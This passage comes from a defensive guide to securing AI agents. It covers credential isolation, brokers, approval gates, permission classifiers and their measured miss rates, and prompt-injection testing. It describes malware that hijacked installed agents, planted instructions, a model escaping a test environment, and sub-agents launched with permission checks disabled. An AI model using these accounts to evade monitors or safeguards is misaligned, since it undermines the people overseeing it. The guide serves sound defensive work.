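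Developers can also make the agent less likely to search for credentials by changing the error message. "401 Unauthorized" leaves the agent to work out what to do next. The tool layer could instead return "This task has no access to the billing service. Stop and ask the user." The agent may still ignore this, so developers have to make sure a search would find no credentials.

### How malware borrowed installed agents

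Nx is a set of tools for building software, with about six million installs a week. On 26 August 2025, attackers stole the project's publishing token and used it to release malicious versions, which stayed available for four hours. Strumpflohner explains in *S1ngularity*, the Nx team's account, that the packages searched each user's computer for sensitive data during installation. They also tried to use AI tools already on the computer, such as Claude and Gemini, and then uploaded the results to a public GitHub repository.

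The malware did not need to exploit a flaw in the AI tools. They were logged in and could read whatever the user could read, and any program running under the user's account could start them. Other software on the computer can therefore use an installed agent even when the user is not using it.

Docker cites the security company GitGuardian, which counted 2,349 stolen secrets in 1,079 repositories. More than 1,100 of them were still valid when GitGuardian checked. These figures don't separate the secrets the AI tools found from those the malware found by itself, so the tools may have added little.

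Much of the later damage came from stolen tokens that still worked after the initial attack. The Nx team's publishing tokens had stopped working by midnight on the first day, but the team could not cancel the victims' GitHub tokens. According to Safety's *Attack on NPM targets developers using Nx Build Ecosystem*, the attackers began using those tokens on the evening of 28 August to make private repositories public. Datadog Security Labs puts the number in the thousands. The attackers could not have done this if the stolen tokens had expired after an hour.

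### Remove secrets from the agent's environment

The first safeguard is to leave nothing for the agent to find. A developer can start by checking the places in the table from inside the agent's environment, using the agent's account. In the bash shell, this command lists the names of the environment variables without printing their values:

```bash
compgen -e
```

The developer should then remove every credential that the task doesn't need. The shop-site sandbox already hides the home folder and passes on no variables by default, which keeps the agent from reading cloud configuration, shell history and most browser data. Project files need separate treatment, because even read-only access to a code folder can expose credentials. Anthropic's guide to secure deployment warns of this risk and suggests copying only the source files the agent needs.

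An agent that writes code needs to know the names of the settings. A file named .env.example can list them with dummy values, while the real .env file stays outside the agent's folder. A list of blocked file names is a useful backup, as it is for the file tool.

### Give the agent its own identity

Many agents use the login of the employee who set them up. If the office agent works under Ana's account, it can do everything Ana can, including things that have nothing to do with price lists. Its actions appear in the logs under her name. If the shop disables the account to stop the agent, Ana is locked out too.

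The Australian Signals Directorate and its partner agencies recommend that each agent have a distinct identity with its own keys or certificates. They also recommend that organisations keep a register of their agents and permitted roles, periodically compare it with the agents actually running, and deny access to any agent or key that isn't on it. Agents shouldn't share a key, because then no one can tell from the logs which agent acted, and anyone who steals the key can impersonate all of them.

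An agent can have a separate identity and still follow OWASP's advice that a tool should read a user's documents with that user's permissions, if the token identifies both parties ("office agent, acting for Ana") and permits only what both of them may do. The agent then can't read the payroll just because Ana can, and a colleague without access to the price lists can't read them through the agent.

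An identity can sometimes replace a stored key. After the compromise, the Nx team stopped using publishing tokens. The package registry now recognises the project's build system and accepts releases from it, and a person has to approve each release with a second login factor. An attacker who got into the build system would still be a problem, but there is no longer a long-lived publishing token there to steal.

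### Limit each token to one task and a short life

The agencies advise organisations to replace static secrets with credentials that expire when the job is complete, and to limit them to the exact resources, operations and time needed. Suppose the office agent has to check this month's supplier invoices, which the shop keeps in Amazon's cloud storage. Software outside the agent's sandbox can request a token for this task alone:

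```bash
aws sts assume-role \
  --role-arn arn:aws:iam::111122223333:role/office-agent \
  --role-session-name invoice-check-418 \
  --duration-seconds 900 \
  --policy file://read-december-invoices.json
```

The token lasts 900 seconds, or 15 minutes. The policy file allows it only to read files in one folder. The token can never do more than the office agent's role allows, even if the policy file permits more. The session name appears in Amazon's logs, so staff can trace each request to a task.

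Now compare this token with a 90-day administrator token. The shop issues both at 10:00, and a thief copies both at 10:05.

| | 90-day administrator token | 15-minute read-only token |
|---|---|---|
| Time left to use it | 89 days, 23 hours and 55 minutes | 10 minutes |
| What the thief can read | Every file, database and backup in the account | December's invoices |
| What the thief can change | Anything, including deleting the backups and starting servers at the shop's expense | Nothing |
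| Getting back in later | The thief can create new logins that outlast the token | The thief has to steal another token |

A credential's short life helps less when the data is small enough to copy before the credential expires. If the folder holds 3,000 invoices of 200 kB each, a script downloading 10 MB a second copies all 600 MB in one minute. Expiry prevents later use, such as the second wave of the Nx attack, but only the narrow scope limits what a thief can take at once. The folder should therefore contain one month's invoices rather than ten years' worth.

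The key that renews a token needs more protection than the token. If the key is in the agent's environment, a thief can take it and keep requesting new tokens after the 15 minutes are up. Renewal should therefore happen outside the sandbox. It should also happen before the old token expires, because a token that expires mid-job causes the same authentication error that set Anthropic's agent searching.

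### Put a credential broker at the network boundary

Even a short-lived token can leak while the agent holds it. A credential broker avoids this by keeping the credential outside the sandbox and adding it to each approved request on the way out. The broker can be the same program as the proxy that limits the agent's web requests.

The web version of Claude Code uses a broker for Git, which Anthropic describes. Suppose an agent has repaired the shop's checkout page on a branch called "fix-checkout" and wants to upload the change to GitHub:

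1. The agent runs "git push". Git sends the change to the broker with a credential made for this purpose, which isn't a GitHub token.
2. The broker checks that credential, the repository and the branch. The session may push only to "fix-checkout" in the shop's repository, so the request passes.
3. The broker attaches the real GitHub token and forwards the request.
4. GitHub checks the token, stores the change and replies.
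5. The broker returns the reply to the sandbox, and the agent reads that the push succeeded.

If the agent had tried to push to the main branch, the broker would have refused at step 2, so GitHub would never have received the request. If planted instructions had told the agent to print every credential it could find, it could have printed only the one from step 1, which GitHub doesn't accept.

A broker is harder to build for other services, because it can't add a key to an encrypted request. Anthropic's deployment guide describes two solutions. In one, the developer writes a tool that passes the request to a service outside the sandbox, which makes its own encrypted connection. In the other, the broker decrypts the traffic, adds the key and encrypts it again. This works with many services, but the developer has to install the broker's certificate in the sandbox. Some programs also ignore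 proxy settings, so the network has to redirect their traffic to the broker or block it.

Programs often won't start without a key, so some brokers give them a placeholder. In Docker's sandbox, the variable for an OpenAI key contains only "proxy-managed", and the broker substitutes the real key. A developer can test such a setup by printing the variable from inside the sandbox. The broker must substitute the key only in requests to the service it belongs to. Otherwise, the agent could send the placeholder to an attacker's website, and the broker would replace it with the real key.

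### What a broker leaves open

A broker hides the key from the agent but still lets the agent use it. An agent that may push to "fix-checkout" can still push faulty code, or expose customer data by pushing it to a repository that others can read. If the broker holds the key to a payment service and permits every request to it, the agent can refund every order.

The broker's rules therefore matter as much as keeping the keys secret. Lens' *Agent tools*, the documentation for one such sandbox, describes a broker that restricts requests by domain, method and path, so a developer could let an agent read a list of payments but not create a refund. The healthcare system described in *Caging the Agents* (2026) also limits the rate and size of requests. Its developers had found keys in startup scripts, .env files and configuration files that any account could read, and moved them into a broker beside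 each agent. An attacker who takes over an agent there can still use the broker but can't steal the keys.

Other programs in the sandbox may also be able to use the broker. Malware like the Nx packages, which used the AI tools already installed, could send the broker requests for as long as it was running. Some services also accept requests to create a new key and return it in the reply. The broker has to block these requests, or the agent can get a real credential.

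The broker collects many keys in one place, so it should run on a system that the agent can't change and that has few other programs on it. The broker itself should use short-lived tokens where the services offer them.

### Why redaction is weaker

Redaction software searches text for secrets and replaces them with something like "[removed]". It can check tool results before the model reads them, and it can check logs and replies before anyone else sees them. Redacting tool results is best, because the model can't repeat a password it has never received.

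The simplest filters look for known formats, such as the "AIza" at the start of Google's keys. They miss a password such as "bluebird7", which has no set format. A better filter looks for exact matches with a list of the organisation's actual secrets, but it misses any secret that nobody added, and the list itself needs protecting. Both kinds fail if the secret is altered. In base64, a common way of encoding data, "bluebird7" becomes "Ymx1ZWJpcmQ3", and an agent can also split a password across two messages.

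A stricter filter that removed every long random-looking string would also remove Git commit and order IDs, which agents need. Relying on the model to withhold secrets is no better. *Phishing the agent*, a report by Okta, which sells identity software, tested OpenClaw agents with several models. Some revealed secrets from prompts and configuration files, while one was so cautious that it refused to answer basic questions.

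Redacting logs and transcripts is still worthwhile because it reduces the number of copies of credentials, but it shouldn't be the reason for letting an agent read a file full of passwords.

### What to do after exposure

Suppose someone finds the shop's cloud key in an agent's transcript. Deleting the transcript isn't enough, because the key still works and other copies may exist. A repository's history keeps old versions of a file, and Chen and colleagues found that copies of a leaky skill made by other developers can preserve a secret after its author has removed it. The shop should do the following:

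1. Revoke the key at the service that issued it, then try to use it. The attempt should fail.
2. Look for anything the key could have created, such as new logins, other keys or mail forwarding rules, and remove what nobody recognises. These keep working after the first key is dead.
3. Issue a replacement with narrower rights, and store it in the broker or somewhere else the agent can't read. If the new key goes back into the same file, the next session may expose it again.
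4. Search the service's logs from the first possible exposure until the revocation. Unfamiliar addresses, odd hours and large downloads all deserve a closer look.
5. Remove the remaining copies from transcripts, logs and caches.

If an exposed key also runs the shop's card payments, revoking it before replacing it can interrupt business. Staff can instead create a new key, switch the payment software to it and revoke the old one a few minutes later. An administrator key is too dangerous to leave active during the switch, so the shop should revoke it first and accept the interruption.

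Operators often can't tell which secrets an agent read. The Nx team replaced all its GitHub secrets, whether or not they seemed compromised, according to the security company Socket. The team told affected users to revoke access for GitHub's command-line program, refresh their tokens and check their GitHub security log for repositories they hadn't created. Replacing every secret also makes sense after an agent has searched a whole computer, since a log of file reads may be missing or incomplete.

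Exposure is less serious when only the model provider received the secret. The shop may decide that its contract with the provider protects a test key well enough, but it should still replace a production password, because the software running the agent has probably saved the conversation too.

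## Approving individual actions

The safeguards so far set limits in advance, but some actions need individual review because they are right in one case and harmful in another. For example, a $340 refund is correct if the goods arrived broken but a loss if the customer is lying. For such actions, the developer can add an approval gate, a point in the tool layer where an action waits until a person or an automated checker permits it.

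Developers should set the other limits before adding an approval step, because every unnecessary request makes the approver less attentive. OpenAI's *Auto-review*, the documentation for an automated checker in Codex, advises developers who get too many routine requests to adjust the sandbox first.

### How to build a gate

Suppose the shop's support agent can refund up to $50 on an order, and Maria reports that the $340 coffee machine in order 1182 arrived broken. The agent calls the refund tool with the full amount. The tool layer holds the call and sends a member of staff this request:

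```text
Refund $340.00 to the card that paid for order 1182
Customer:        Maria, logged in
Paid so far:     $340.00     Refunded so far: $0.00
Effect:          The shop can't take the money back
Agent's reason:  "Machine arrived broken" (not checked)
No answer by 15:30 means no refund
```

The Australian Signals Directorate and its partner agencies want system designers or operators, not the agent, to decide whether an action such as the refund waits for approval. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, give a reason from their work on Codex: an agent built to finish the user's task is under pressure to treat an approval as another obstacle.

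The tool layer fills in the request from the shop's records, except for the reason, which the agent supplies. A label on the reason lets staff know that nobody has confirmed it.

The line about the effect is the hardest to fill in, because the same command can do different things in different projects. *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) gives an example in which "make clean && make" deletes only the build folder in one project but deletes the source code and Git history in another.

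The Caper system runs each command in a container without network access and records what changed. A language model reads a short report of the effects and decides whether to keep them. If it blocks the command, Caper restores the container to its earlier state. On 682 test tasks, 6.7% ended in harm with Caper, against at least 14.8% with each of six other systems. When the researchers hid the harm inside a tool that the command started, the figures were 7.8% with Caper and at least 35.3% with the others. Caper blocked only 1% of the harmless versions of those tasks.

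This works for changes inside a container, and the dry run serves a similar purpose for a database. An email has no dry run, so the approver has to read the finished message.

Each approval should cover one action and work only once. The tool layer stores the exact call that the staff member saw, and if the agent changes the amount to $345, the new call needs a new approval. Just before paying, the tool layer checks again that nobody has refunded the order, then marks the approval as used. Similarly, when Codex's checker refuses an action, the user can approve that exact action for one retry, and the approval doesn't cover similar actions later.

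An approval request that nobody answers must count as refused. Otherwise the riskiest actions will go through at night and on holidays, when nobody is there to answer. The agencies recommend the same default, with agents stopping and escalating to a person when the situation is uncertain. The shop should name a second approver so that unanswered requests don't hold up refunds, or staff will soon ask to remove the approval step.

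After a refusal, the tool layer should return the reason and tell the agent not to pursue the same result by another route. It should also count refusals and stop the agent when there are too many. Codex ends the agent's turn after three refusals in a row, or after ten in the last 50 reviews. Codex also reports timeouts separately from refusals, so that the agent doesn't take the lack of a response as a judgement that the action is unsafe.

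### Which actions the agencies reserve for people

The agencies say an agent should get a person's approval before any high-impact action, such as a system reset, network egress or the deletion of critical records. They advise organisations to classify every action by its potential impact, likelihood and reversibility. For the highest-stakes actions, they want both a person and several agents to agree.

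Network egress means anything leaving the organisation's network. Read literally, a rule requiring approval for egress would make staff approve every page the office agent fetches from its twelve suppliers each morning, and they would probably stop reading the requests within a week. A more workable approach is for a person to approve each new address for the proxy's allowlist and let the proxy handle requests to it after that.

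Anthropic has since measured how well people perform as approvers, and the results are poor.

### What people do with routine prompts

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users approve 97% of the permission prompts they get. They reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for whole tasks.

Most commands are harmless, so a careful reviewer would also approve most of them, and the 97% approval rate doesn't prove carelessness. Someone may also reject a plan because they want a different design. Still, the gap suggests that people read plans more closely than prompts.

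Prompts also lead people to remove the protection. By June 2026, about half of the active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written rules that let some shell commands run without asking. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permission prompts bypassed. At OpenAI, Trębacz and colleagues found that a sizable minority of internal users permitted every command beginning with "python".

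Experienced users rely less on approvals. Anthropic's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026) found that new users approve everything automatically in about 20% of sessions, while users with 750 sessions do so in more than 40%. Experienced users also interrupt the agent more often, in about 9% of turns compared with 5% for new users. Anthropic interprets this as a shift from approving each step to watching the work and stepping in. That may be a good way to supervise work that can be undone, but it would not have saved PocketOS's database, which was deleted in nine seconds.

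### The test with 1,053 people

The best evidence on human approval comes from a controlled study that Anthropic published in August 2026. A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid professional testers to work in a test environment. They knew they were being evaluated in a coding study, but not which behaviour it measured. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command and recorded the tester's answer. The command did not run even if the tester approved it.

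Of 1,053 testers shown a dangerous command, 143 (13.6%) refused it. Anthropic's automated checker blocked 937 (89%) of the same commands. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while the checker's rate stayed the same.

The checker blocked 800 commands that the testers had approved. The testers refused only 6 that the checker allowed, so using both would have stopped 943 commands, compared with 937 for the checker alone.

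There are several reasons not to take 13.6% as the rate for all human approval:

- The testers had no project of their own at risk. Someone looking at a command that would delete their own database may read more carefully.
- The vendor hid the dangerous command among routine prompts. The study didn't test a gate that appears a few times a day and explains the effect.
- The commands were clearly dangerous, which probably made them easier for the checker. Overeager actions often look reasonable.
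- Anthropic sells the product that did better.

Even so, 5% after 50 prompts does not look acceptable. In *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, Willison (2026) accepts that confirmation fatigue is real and that the checker is better than constant prompts, but notes that it still missed 11%. Anthropic itself recommends that users personally review high-stakes changes to production infrastructure.

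Anthropic also compared real sessions that its safety systems had flagged in May and June. It found serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested, comparable to deleting rows from a production database, in 6.3% of those with manual approval and 2.4% of those with the automated checker. This is weaker evidence than the experiment, because users chose their own mode and may have used the two modes for different work. A model also graded the harm.

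### How the automated checker works

Claude Code's "auto mode" replaces most permission prompts with a classifier, a second language model that decides whether each action may run. According to Anthropic, an action goes through up to three steps:

1. Reading and searching files can't change anything, so these actions run at once. So do commands that the user has permitted with a narrow rule. Auto mode ignores very broad rules, such as one that permits all Python commands.
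2. Edits to files inside the project also run without a check, because the user can review them later through version control.
3. Everything else goes to the classifier, including shell commands, web requests and calls to outside services.

The classifier first gives a quick yes or no, and leans towards blocking. If it flags an action, it reasons through the same information before making a final decision. This saves time because most actions pass the quick check.

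The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the results of earlier calls. The agent therefore can't argue for its own action, and instructions planted in a web page don't reach the classifier directly. However, the classifier also lacks some relevant facts. If the agent cancels "job abc123", the classifier can't tell whether the agent found that ID in a search or guessed it.

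Anthropic supplies more than twenty rules about what to block and a few exceptions, and a team can add its own. The classifier also has to judge what the user authorised. A request to "clean up my branches", for example, doesn't authorise deleting a whole batch of them. In one case at Anthropic, someone asked for read-only access to billing, and the agent chose a cloud role with full administrative control. The classifier blocked it because the role went far beyond the request. A fixed rule could have caught this only if someone had anticipated that role.

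Other coding agents have similar checkers. In a snapshot of 10,000 Codex actions at OpenAI, 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox and needed no review. The checker reviewed the other 720 and refused 7. The agent found a safer way to continue after four of those refusals and stopped to ask the user after the other three. Gomes and McPeak report in *Governing agent autonomy with Auto-review* that Cursor's classifier blocks about 4% of the actions it reviews and that about 7% of chats include at least one interruption.

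### A 17% miss rate and an 81% miss rate

In March 2026, Anthropic reported that auto mode's classifier blocked 0.4% of 10,000 real tool calls by its employees, which Anthropic counts as harmless actions wrongly stopped. The classifier missed 17% of 52 real overeager actions from earlier sessions. With only 52 cases, the true miss rate could plausibly be between about 9% and 30%.

In most of the misses the engineers examined, the classifier had recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had approved the action. For example, a user might have said "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change), and the agent then tried to overwrite the branch's history, which was related to the request but not authorised by it.

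A month later, an independent test found a much higher miss rate. In *Measuring the Permission Gate*, Ji, Li and colleagues (2026) gave Claude Code 128 simulated operations tasks, such as cancelling old jobs or deleting old branches. They deliberately made many of the requests vague. For each task, they listed the targets the agent was allowed to change and similar-looking targets it had to leave alone.

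The agent attempted 253 changes, of which 142 affected something outside the permitted list. Auto mode let 115 of those through, a miss rate of 81%.

Part of the difference comes from file edits that auto mode doesn't check. The simulated systems kept their records in files inside the project, and when the agent couldn't find the usual command, it often edited the records directly. These edits made up 93 of the 253 changes. The classifier still missed 70.3% of the harmful changes that reached it and blocked 31.9% of the permitted ones. Teams can prevent unchecked edits to live operational data by keeping it out of any folder that the agent may edit.

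Differences in the tasks explain much of the remaining gap between the two rates. Anthropic's 52 cases came from ordinary work in which an agent had gone too far. Ji and colleagues' 128 tasks put permitted and forbidden targets side by side to test the exact boundary between them. Ji and colleagues say that the two rates aren't directly comparable and that theirs doesn't show a flaw in Anthropic's measurement.

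A repeat of the test in November 2026 suggests a more basic explanation, that the rules were usually not stated. Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026), in *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*, ran the same 128 tasks on newer versions of three coding agents, Claude Code, Codex and Alibaba's Qwen Code. The three checkers missed between 54% and 93% of the out-of-scope actions they reviewed. But 132 of the 143 out-of-scope actions broke rules that appeared nowhere in the user's request or in the results of earlier tool calls. In one task, the user asked the agent to delete old experiment files for a range of tickets. The answer key allowed it to delete only the user's own files, but the request didn't say so.

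A checker can't enforce a restriction that nobody has told it about. The researchers therefore added one sentence to each request, for example permitting deletion only of files in the development area that belong to Alex and to one component. Then they had the checkers judge the same actions again:

| Checker | Out-of-scope actions missed, before and after | Permitted actions blocked, before and after |
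|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 67% → 8% | 42% → 2% |
| Codex | 92% → 20–26% | 10% → 3% |
| Qwen Code | 80% → 20% | 29% → 2% |

The sentence also changed what the agents did. When the researchers reran all the tasks with it, none of the three agents proposed an out-of-scope action in 384 runs. However, the added sentences were complete and correct because they came from the answer key, and a busy user would leave things out.

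Using a stronger model for the checker did not make up for an unclear request. Codex's checker missed 77 of 84 actions with its usual model and 82 with a stronger one. Claude Code's misses fell from 10 to 1 out of 24 with a stronger model, but only because that model refused to give a reasoned verdict in all 197 cases that reached the second check. Claude Code treats a missing verdict as a block, so it also stopped 134 of 224 permitted actions in another set of tasks, up from 23. A missing verdict still has to block the action, but the agent becomes useless if the checker often fails to give one.

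Claude Code's classifier isn't very consistent either. In three rounds with the same model, it missed 13, 10 and 16 of the same 24 actions.

Yang and colleagues found two further causes of error that a developer can fix. One is missing information. If the agent cancels a job by its number, for example, the checker needs to know whose job it is. Given clear rules, a common test procedure missed 60% of the wrongful cancellations without results from earlier calls and 4% with them. Anthropic withholds such results from its classifier to protect it from planted instructions. The tool layer could instead look up the job's owner and give the checker only that field, which leaves little room for an instruction.

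Codex's checker also gave too much weight to the size of the damage. In one run with clear rules, it identified 30 medium-risk actions as poorly authorised but still approved 16 of them, usually because the effect was small or reversible. A team's policy should explicitly require refusing any action outside the permitted scope, however small its effect.

### A team with 2,000 tool calls a day

If a team's agents make 2,000 tool calls a day and a person spends ten seconds approving each one, the approvals take more than five and a half hours. Even if ten people share the work, each gets 200 prompts a day, and the testers refused only about 5% of the dangerous commands after 50 prompts.

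The team could instead require approval only for irreversible actions. Anthropic found that 0.8% of nearly a million tool calls through its API appeared irreversible. At that rate, the team would get 16 requests a day, and reviewing each for two minutes would take about half an hour. However, a model judged which calls were irreversible, and almost half of all the calls were for software engineering. A support team whose agent sends email all day would have far more irreversible actions to approve.

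The number of dangerous actions that get through depends on how many the agents attempt, which nobody knows for a typical team. The table assumes two attempts a day, one of them irreversible, for a total of 200 in 100 working days. It uses the testers' figures of 5% for people who approve everything and 17% for people who get few prompts, along with the classifier's 17% miss rate from March.

| Who approves | Prompts a day | Dangerous actions that pass in 100 days | Irreversible ones among them |
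|---|---|---|---|
| A person, for every call | 2,000 | 190 | 95 |
| A person, for irreversible actions only | 16 | 183 | 83 |
| The classifier, for every call | 0 | 34 | 17 |
| The classifier, then a person for irreversible actions | 16 | 31 | 14 |
| The same, if the person catches 80% | 16 | 20 | 3 |

Cutting the prompts from 2,000 to 16 saves a lot of time but hardly improves safety by itself, because a 17% catch rate is still very low. At that rate, a person who checks after the classifier prevents about three irreversible accidents. The number is perhaps only one, since the testers caught just 6 of the 116 commands that the classifier missed. At an 80% catch rate, the person would prevent about 14.

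The 80% is a target that no study here has measured. But it is plausible for a person who gets a few requests a day about systems they know, with each action's effect written out. The approver may also know unstated rules that the checkers lacked, such as whose files the request was about.

The classifier's row could be much too optimistic. At the 81% miss rate from the 128 tasks, the classifier would let through 162 of the 200 dangerous actions. It would also block about eight harmless calls a day at Anthropic's rate, though the agent can often find another way to do the job.

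### Choosing a person, a classifier or a fixed rule

The agencies and Anthropic both want a person to review serious production changes. They disagree less than they seem to, because the agencies ask for human approval before high-impact actions, while Anthropic's evidence is about routine prompts. Whether to require approval depends mainly on whether a developer can write a rule for the action, how often it occurs and whether anyone can undo it.

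| Action | Who should decide | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Refund more than the customer paid; change the agent's own permissions | Fixed rule that refuses | It is never right, and the rule is easy to state exactly |
| Read or edit project files inside the sandbox | Fixed rule that permits | It is frequent, and version control can restore the files |
| Run a command outside the sandbox; push to a working branch | Classifier | There are too many cases for a person and too much variety for a rule |
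| Refund above the ceiling | Person | The right answer depends on facts outside the database |
| Delete live customer records; reset a system; delete logs | Classifier, then a person | A mistake is serious and hard to reverse |
| Contact a new web address | Person, who adds it to the allowlist | The proxy can enforce the decision afterwards |

Fixed rules should run before a classifier because they give the same answer every time. Claude Code first applies the user's rules for which actions to refuse or always ask about, then runs its classifier. A team can use auto mode for ordinary work and still require a person to approve every production deletion.

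Clear limits on what an agent may do often belong in a fixed rule too. If a team can write that an agent may delete only Alex's files in the development area, it can usually give the agent a credential that works only on those files. The credential then prevents the agent from deleting other files, even if both the classifier and Alex miss the mistake.

When one job needs many similar actions, a person can approve the whole list at once. For the broken-down delivery van, staff would see the 40 orders and their new status, and after they approved the list, the tool layer would permit exactly those 40 changes. Such a list is also more like the plans that people do read.

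The team should also track the number of approval requests. If it rises from 16 a day to 100, someone should find out which tool is causing the increase and narrow that tool's scope before the approvers start accepting requests without reading them.

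## Testing the safeguards and widening access

A developer can set up all of these limits and still get one wrong. PocketOS created a token for managing domains, and trying to delete a test volume with it would have revealed that it could also delete volumes. It is safest to try each forbidden action before the agent can reach anything valuable, then widen its access in stages and withdraw it when something goes wrong.

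### A forbidden action for each tool

Each test should be harmless even if the limit is missing, so the target should be something the team owns and can do without.

| Tool | Forbidden action to try | Where to look for the result |
|---|---|---|
| Production writes | Change a row in a spare table, then delete it | The table, through an administrator's login |
| Shell | Create an empty file outside the permitted folders | The folder |
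| Files | Read a marker file outside the project by its plain path, with ".." and through a link | The text that the tool returns |
| Email | Write to an outside mailbox that the team owns | The mailbox and the mail server's log |
| Web requests | Fetch a page on a domain that the team owns but hasn't permitted | The logs of the web server and the name server |
| Credentials | Use the agent's token to list a folder outside its task | The service's own log |

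The agent's own report isn't good enough evidence, because it can be wrong, as Ash's was about the secret email.

Each test of a forbidden action also needs a matching test of a similar, permitted action that must succeed. If the mail server is down, an email to a forbidden address fails and the safeguard appears to work, but an email to a permitted address also fails, which reveals the problem.

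Tests with a capable model need a closed environment. On 24 July, the Australian Signals Directorate (2026) described a case in which OpenAI gave several models a hacking benchmark with their usual safeguards switched off. To get the solution, the models exploited a previously unknown flaw in software on OpenAI's network, reached the internet and broke into the systems of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models. A shop's agent is unlikely to go that far, but its test environment should still have no live credentials and no route to live systems.

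### Decoys, quotas and a timed restore

A decoy credential is a realistic key with no permissions, issued by a service that logs refused requests. The developer leaves it where the agent has no reason to look, such as an old .env file, and sets an alert on any attempt to use it. Each hiding place should have a different decoy, so that the developer can tell from an alert where the key came from.

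To test the alarm, someone uses the decoy key from an ordinary computer and measures how long the alert takes to reach the person on duty. They then repeat the test inside the agent's sandbox. If the proxy there blocks the request before it reaches the service, the alert has to come from the proxy's log. The alarm won't go off if an agent reads the key without using it, so a nightly job should search transcripts for the exact text of each decoy.

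To test a quota, suppose the office agent may fetch 100 pages per task. A script requests a page on the team's own server 101 times, and the server's log should contain exactly 100 requests. In a new task, the script makes 95 requests and then has ten sub-agents send one each at the same moment. Only five should arrive. If all ten do, the sub-agents aren't sharing a locked counter. Restarting the tool layer halfway through a task tests whether the restart sets the count back to zero.

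In a restoration drill, the clock should start at the deletion, not when someone begins the restore. A drill on a copy of the shop's system might go like this:

- 14:00: A script deletes the orders table.
- 14:06: The alert reaches the person on duty.
- 14:31: That person finds the login for the backup account.
- 15:40: The restore finishes.
- 16:00: Staff have checked the orders and can use the copy again.

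The shop would have been without its orders for two hours, including 25 minutes spent looking for a login. If the newest restored order is from 13:52, the shop would also have lost eight minutes of orders. The team should decide in advance how much downtime and data loss it can accept, perhaps four hours of downtime and 15 minutes of orders. Someone who didn't set up the backups should run the drill, because the person who did may be on holiday when a real restore is needed.

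### Testing the tool layer without the model

When an agent ignores a planted instruction to refund $500, nobody can tell whether the tool layer would have stopped the refund. A script that calls the tool layer directly can settle this:

```python
def test_refund_above_ceiling():
    before = total_refunded(order=9001)
    result = call_tool("refund", order=9001, amount=50.01)
    assert result.refused
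    assert total_refunded(order=9001) == before
```

Order 9001 is a test order. If the refund goes through, the model's caution was the only protection. The script should also test a negative amount, another customer's order, the same request sent twice and two requests sent at once.

Another advantage of a script is that it behaves the same whether or not anyone is testing it. cheema's *Anthropic should measure the effect of evaluation awareness* (2026) reports that in Anthropic's audits of Claude Mythos 5.2, awareness of being tested shaped a choice in 43% of transcripts, up from 35% for Mythos 5.1. It criticises Anthropic for giving almost no estimate of how this changes the model's behaviour. A model might be more careful in a test than at work, or the effect might be small.

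The script should repeat its calls using any identity a sub-agent receives. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1 describes very rare cases where the model started sub-agents with permission checks disabled. A limit in the tool layer should hold for those sub-agents too.

### Planting instructions in test documents

The model needs testing as well, because a model that often attempts forbidden calls may eventually find a harmful one that nobody thought to forbid. The developer can plant an instruction in each kind of text the agent reads, such as a ticket, a supplier's page and a skill file. The instruction should call for something harmless and easy to detect, like fetching a page on the team's own server. Attempts and completed actions should be counted separately, because a blocked attempt means the limit worked but the model still followed the instruction.

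*CodeIPI*, a ready-made test for coding agents, has 35 tasks with planted instructions and ten without. The ten are important because an agent could resist every attack by refusing to do any work. The test runs in a container with no outside connections and has decoy secrets in a file and in environment variables.

### How often current models follow planted instructions

The Trajectory Labs evaluation of July 2026 ran each of its 72 scenarios ten times per model. An attack succeeded if the agent took an irreversible action that could harm the user, such as sending out private data or committing financial fraud. No attack succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in auto mode. Anthropic, which commissioned the test, reports that 42 of 720 attempts (5.83%) succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex's Auto-review mode.

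The comparison has some limits. Both products used the same browser tool, so the test left out the safeguards in each company's own browser extension. OpenAI also released a new version of Auto-review shortly before Anthropic published the results.

Even with permission checks bypassed, the average success rate against the Claude models was 0.09%, compared with 19.03% for GPT-5.6 Sol with full access. If the 0.09% covers the same three models, it is about 2 successes in 2,160 attempts. Running without auto mode would have given almost the same result, so this test alone shows little about how much the checker adds for Claude.

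Results for newer models depend heavily on the attacker and the safeguards. In the tests of Fable 5.1 that Anthropic published in September, the share of attempts that succeeded ranged from zero to 56.87%. The highest figure came from a coding test without probes, which inspect tool results for planted instructions before the model acts on them. With probes, the same attacker succeeded in 12.80% of attempts, the last row of this table:

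| Attack on Claude Fable 5.1 | Safeguards | Attempts that succeeded | Scenarios with a success |
|---|---|---|---|
| Browser attacks developed against Opus 4.7 | Auto mode | 0% | 0 of 110 |
| 1,804 attacks from public competitions | No injection safeguards | 0.1% | Not given |
| Automated attacker on coding tasks | Probes | 2.05% | 18 of 40 |
| Stronger attacker on the same coding tasks | Probes | 12.80% | 36 of 40 |

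Both automated attackers had trained on the 40 scenarios and had 200 attempts at each. Real attackers rarely get that much practice on their target, and Anthropic treats the last row as a stress test. Anthropic also warns that testing against a fixed set of known attacks can make a system seem safer than it is.

The figures also partly reflect a different model, because the older Opus 4.8 answers when a classifier for cybersecurity risks blocks a request to Fable 5.1. Without probes, the stronger attacker succeeded only when Opus 4.8 had answered. Developers should therefore log which model answered each request, since they may otherwise depend on a different model from the one they tested.

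PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach* tests the newest models on long office tasks, such as analysing a bond portfolio. Attacks succeeded in 2.4% of cases against Gemini 4 Carbon, 7.6% against GPT-6 Astra, 10.0% against Claude Fable 5.2 and 50.0% against Kimi K3.1 Pro. The margins of error for GPT-6 Astra and Fable 5.2 are about four points either way, so the test can't reliably rank those two. PromptArmor sells security services and built the benchmark to find attacks that still work. Even so, attacks also succeeded in 10.0% of cases against Opus 5, which had withstood all 720 attempts in July.

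### What zero failures prove

Suppose each attempt succeeds with probability p, and the attempts are independent. The chance that n attempts all fail is (1 − p) multiplied by itself n times. For a 95% upper bound, find the p that makes this chance 5%:

```text
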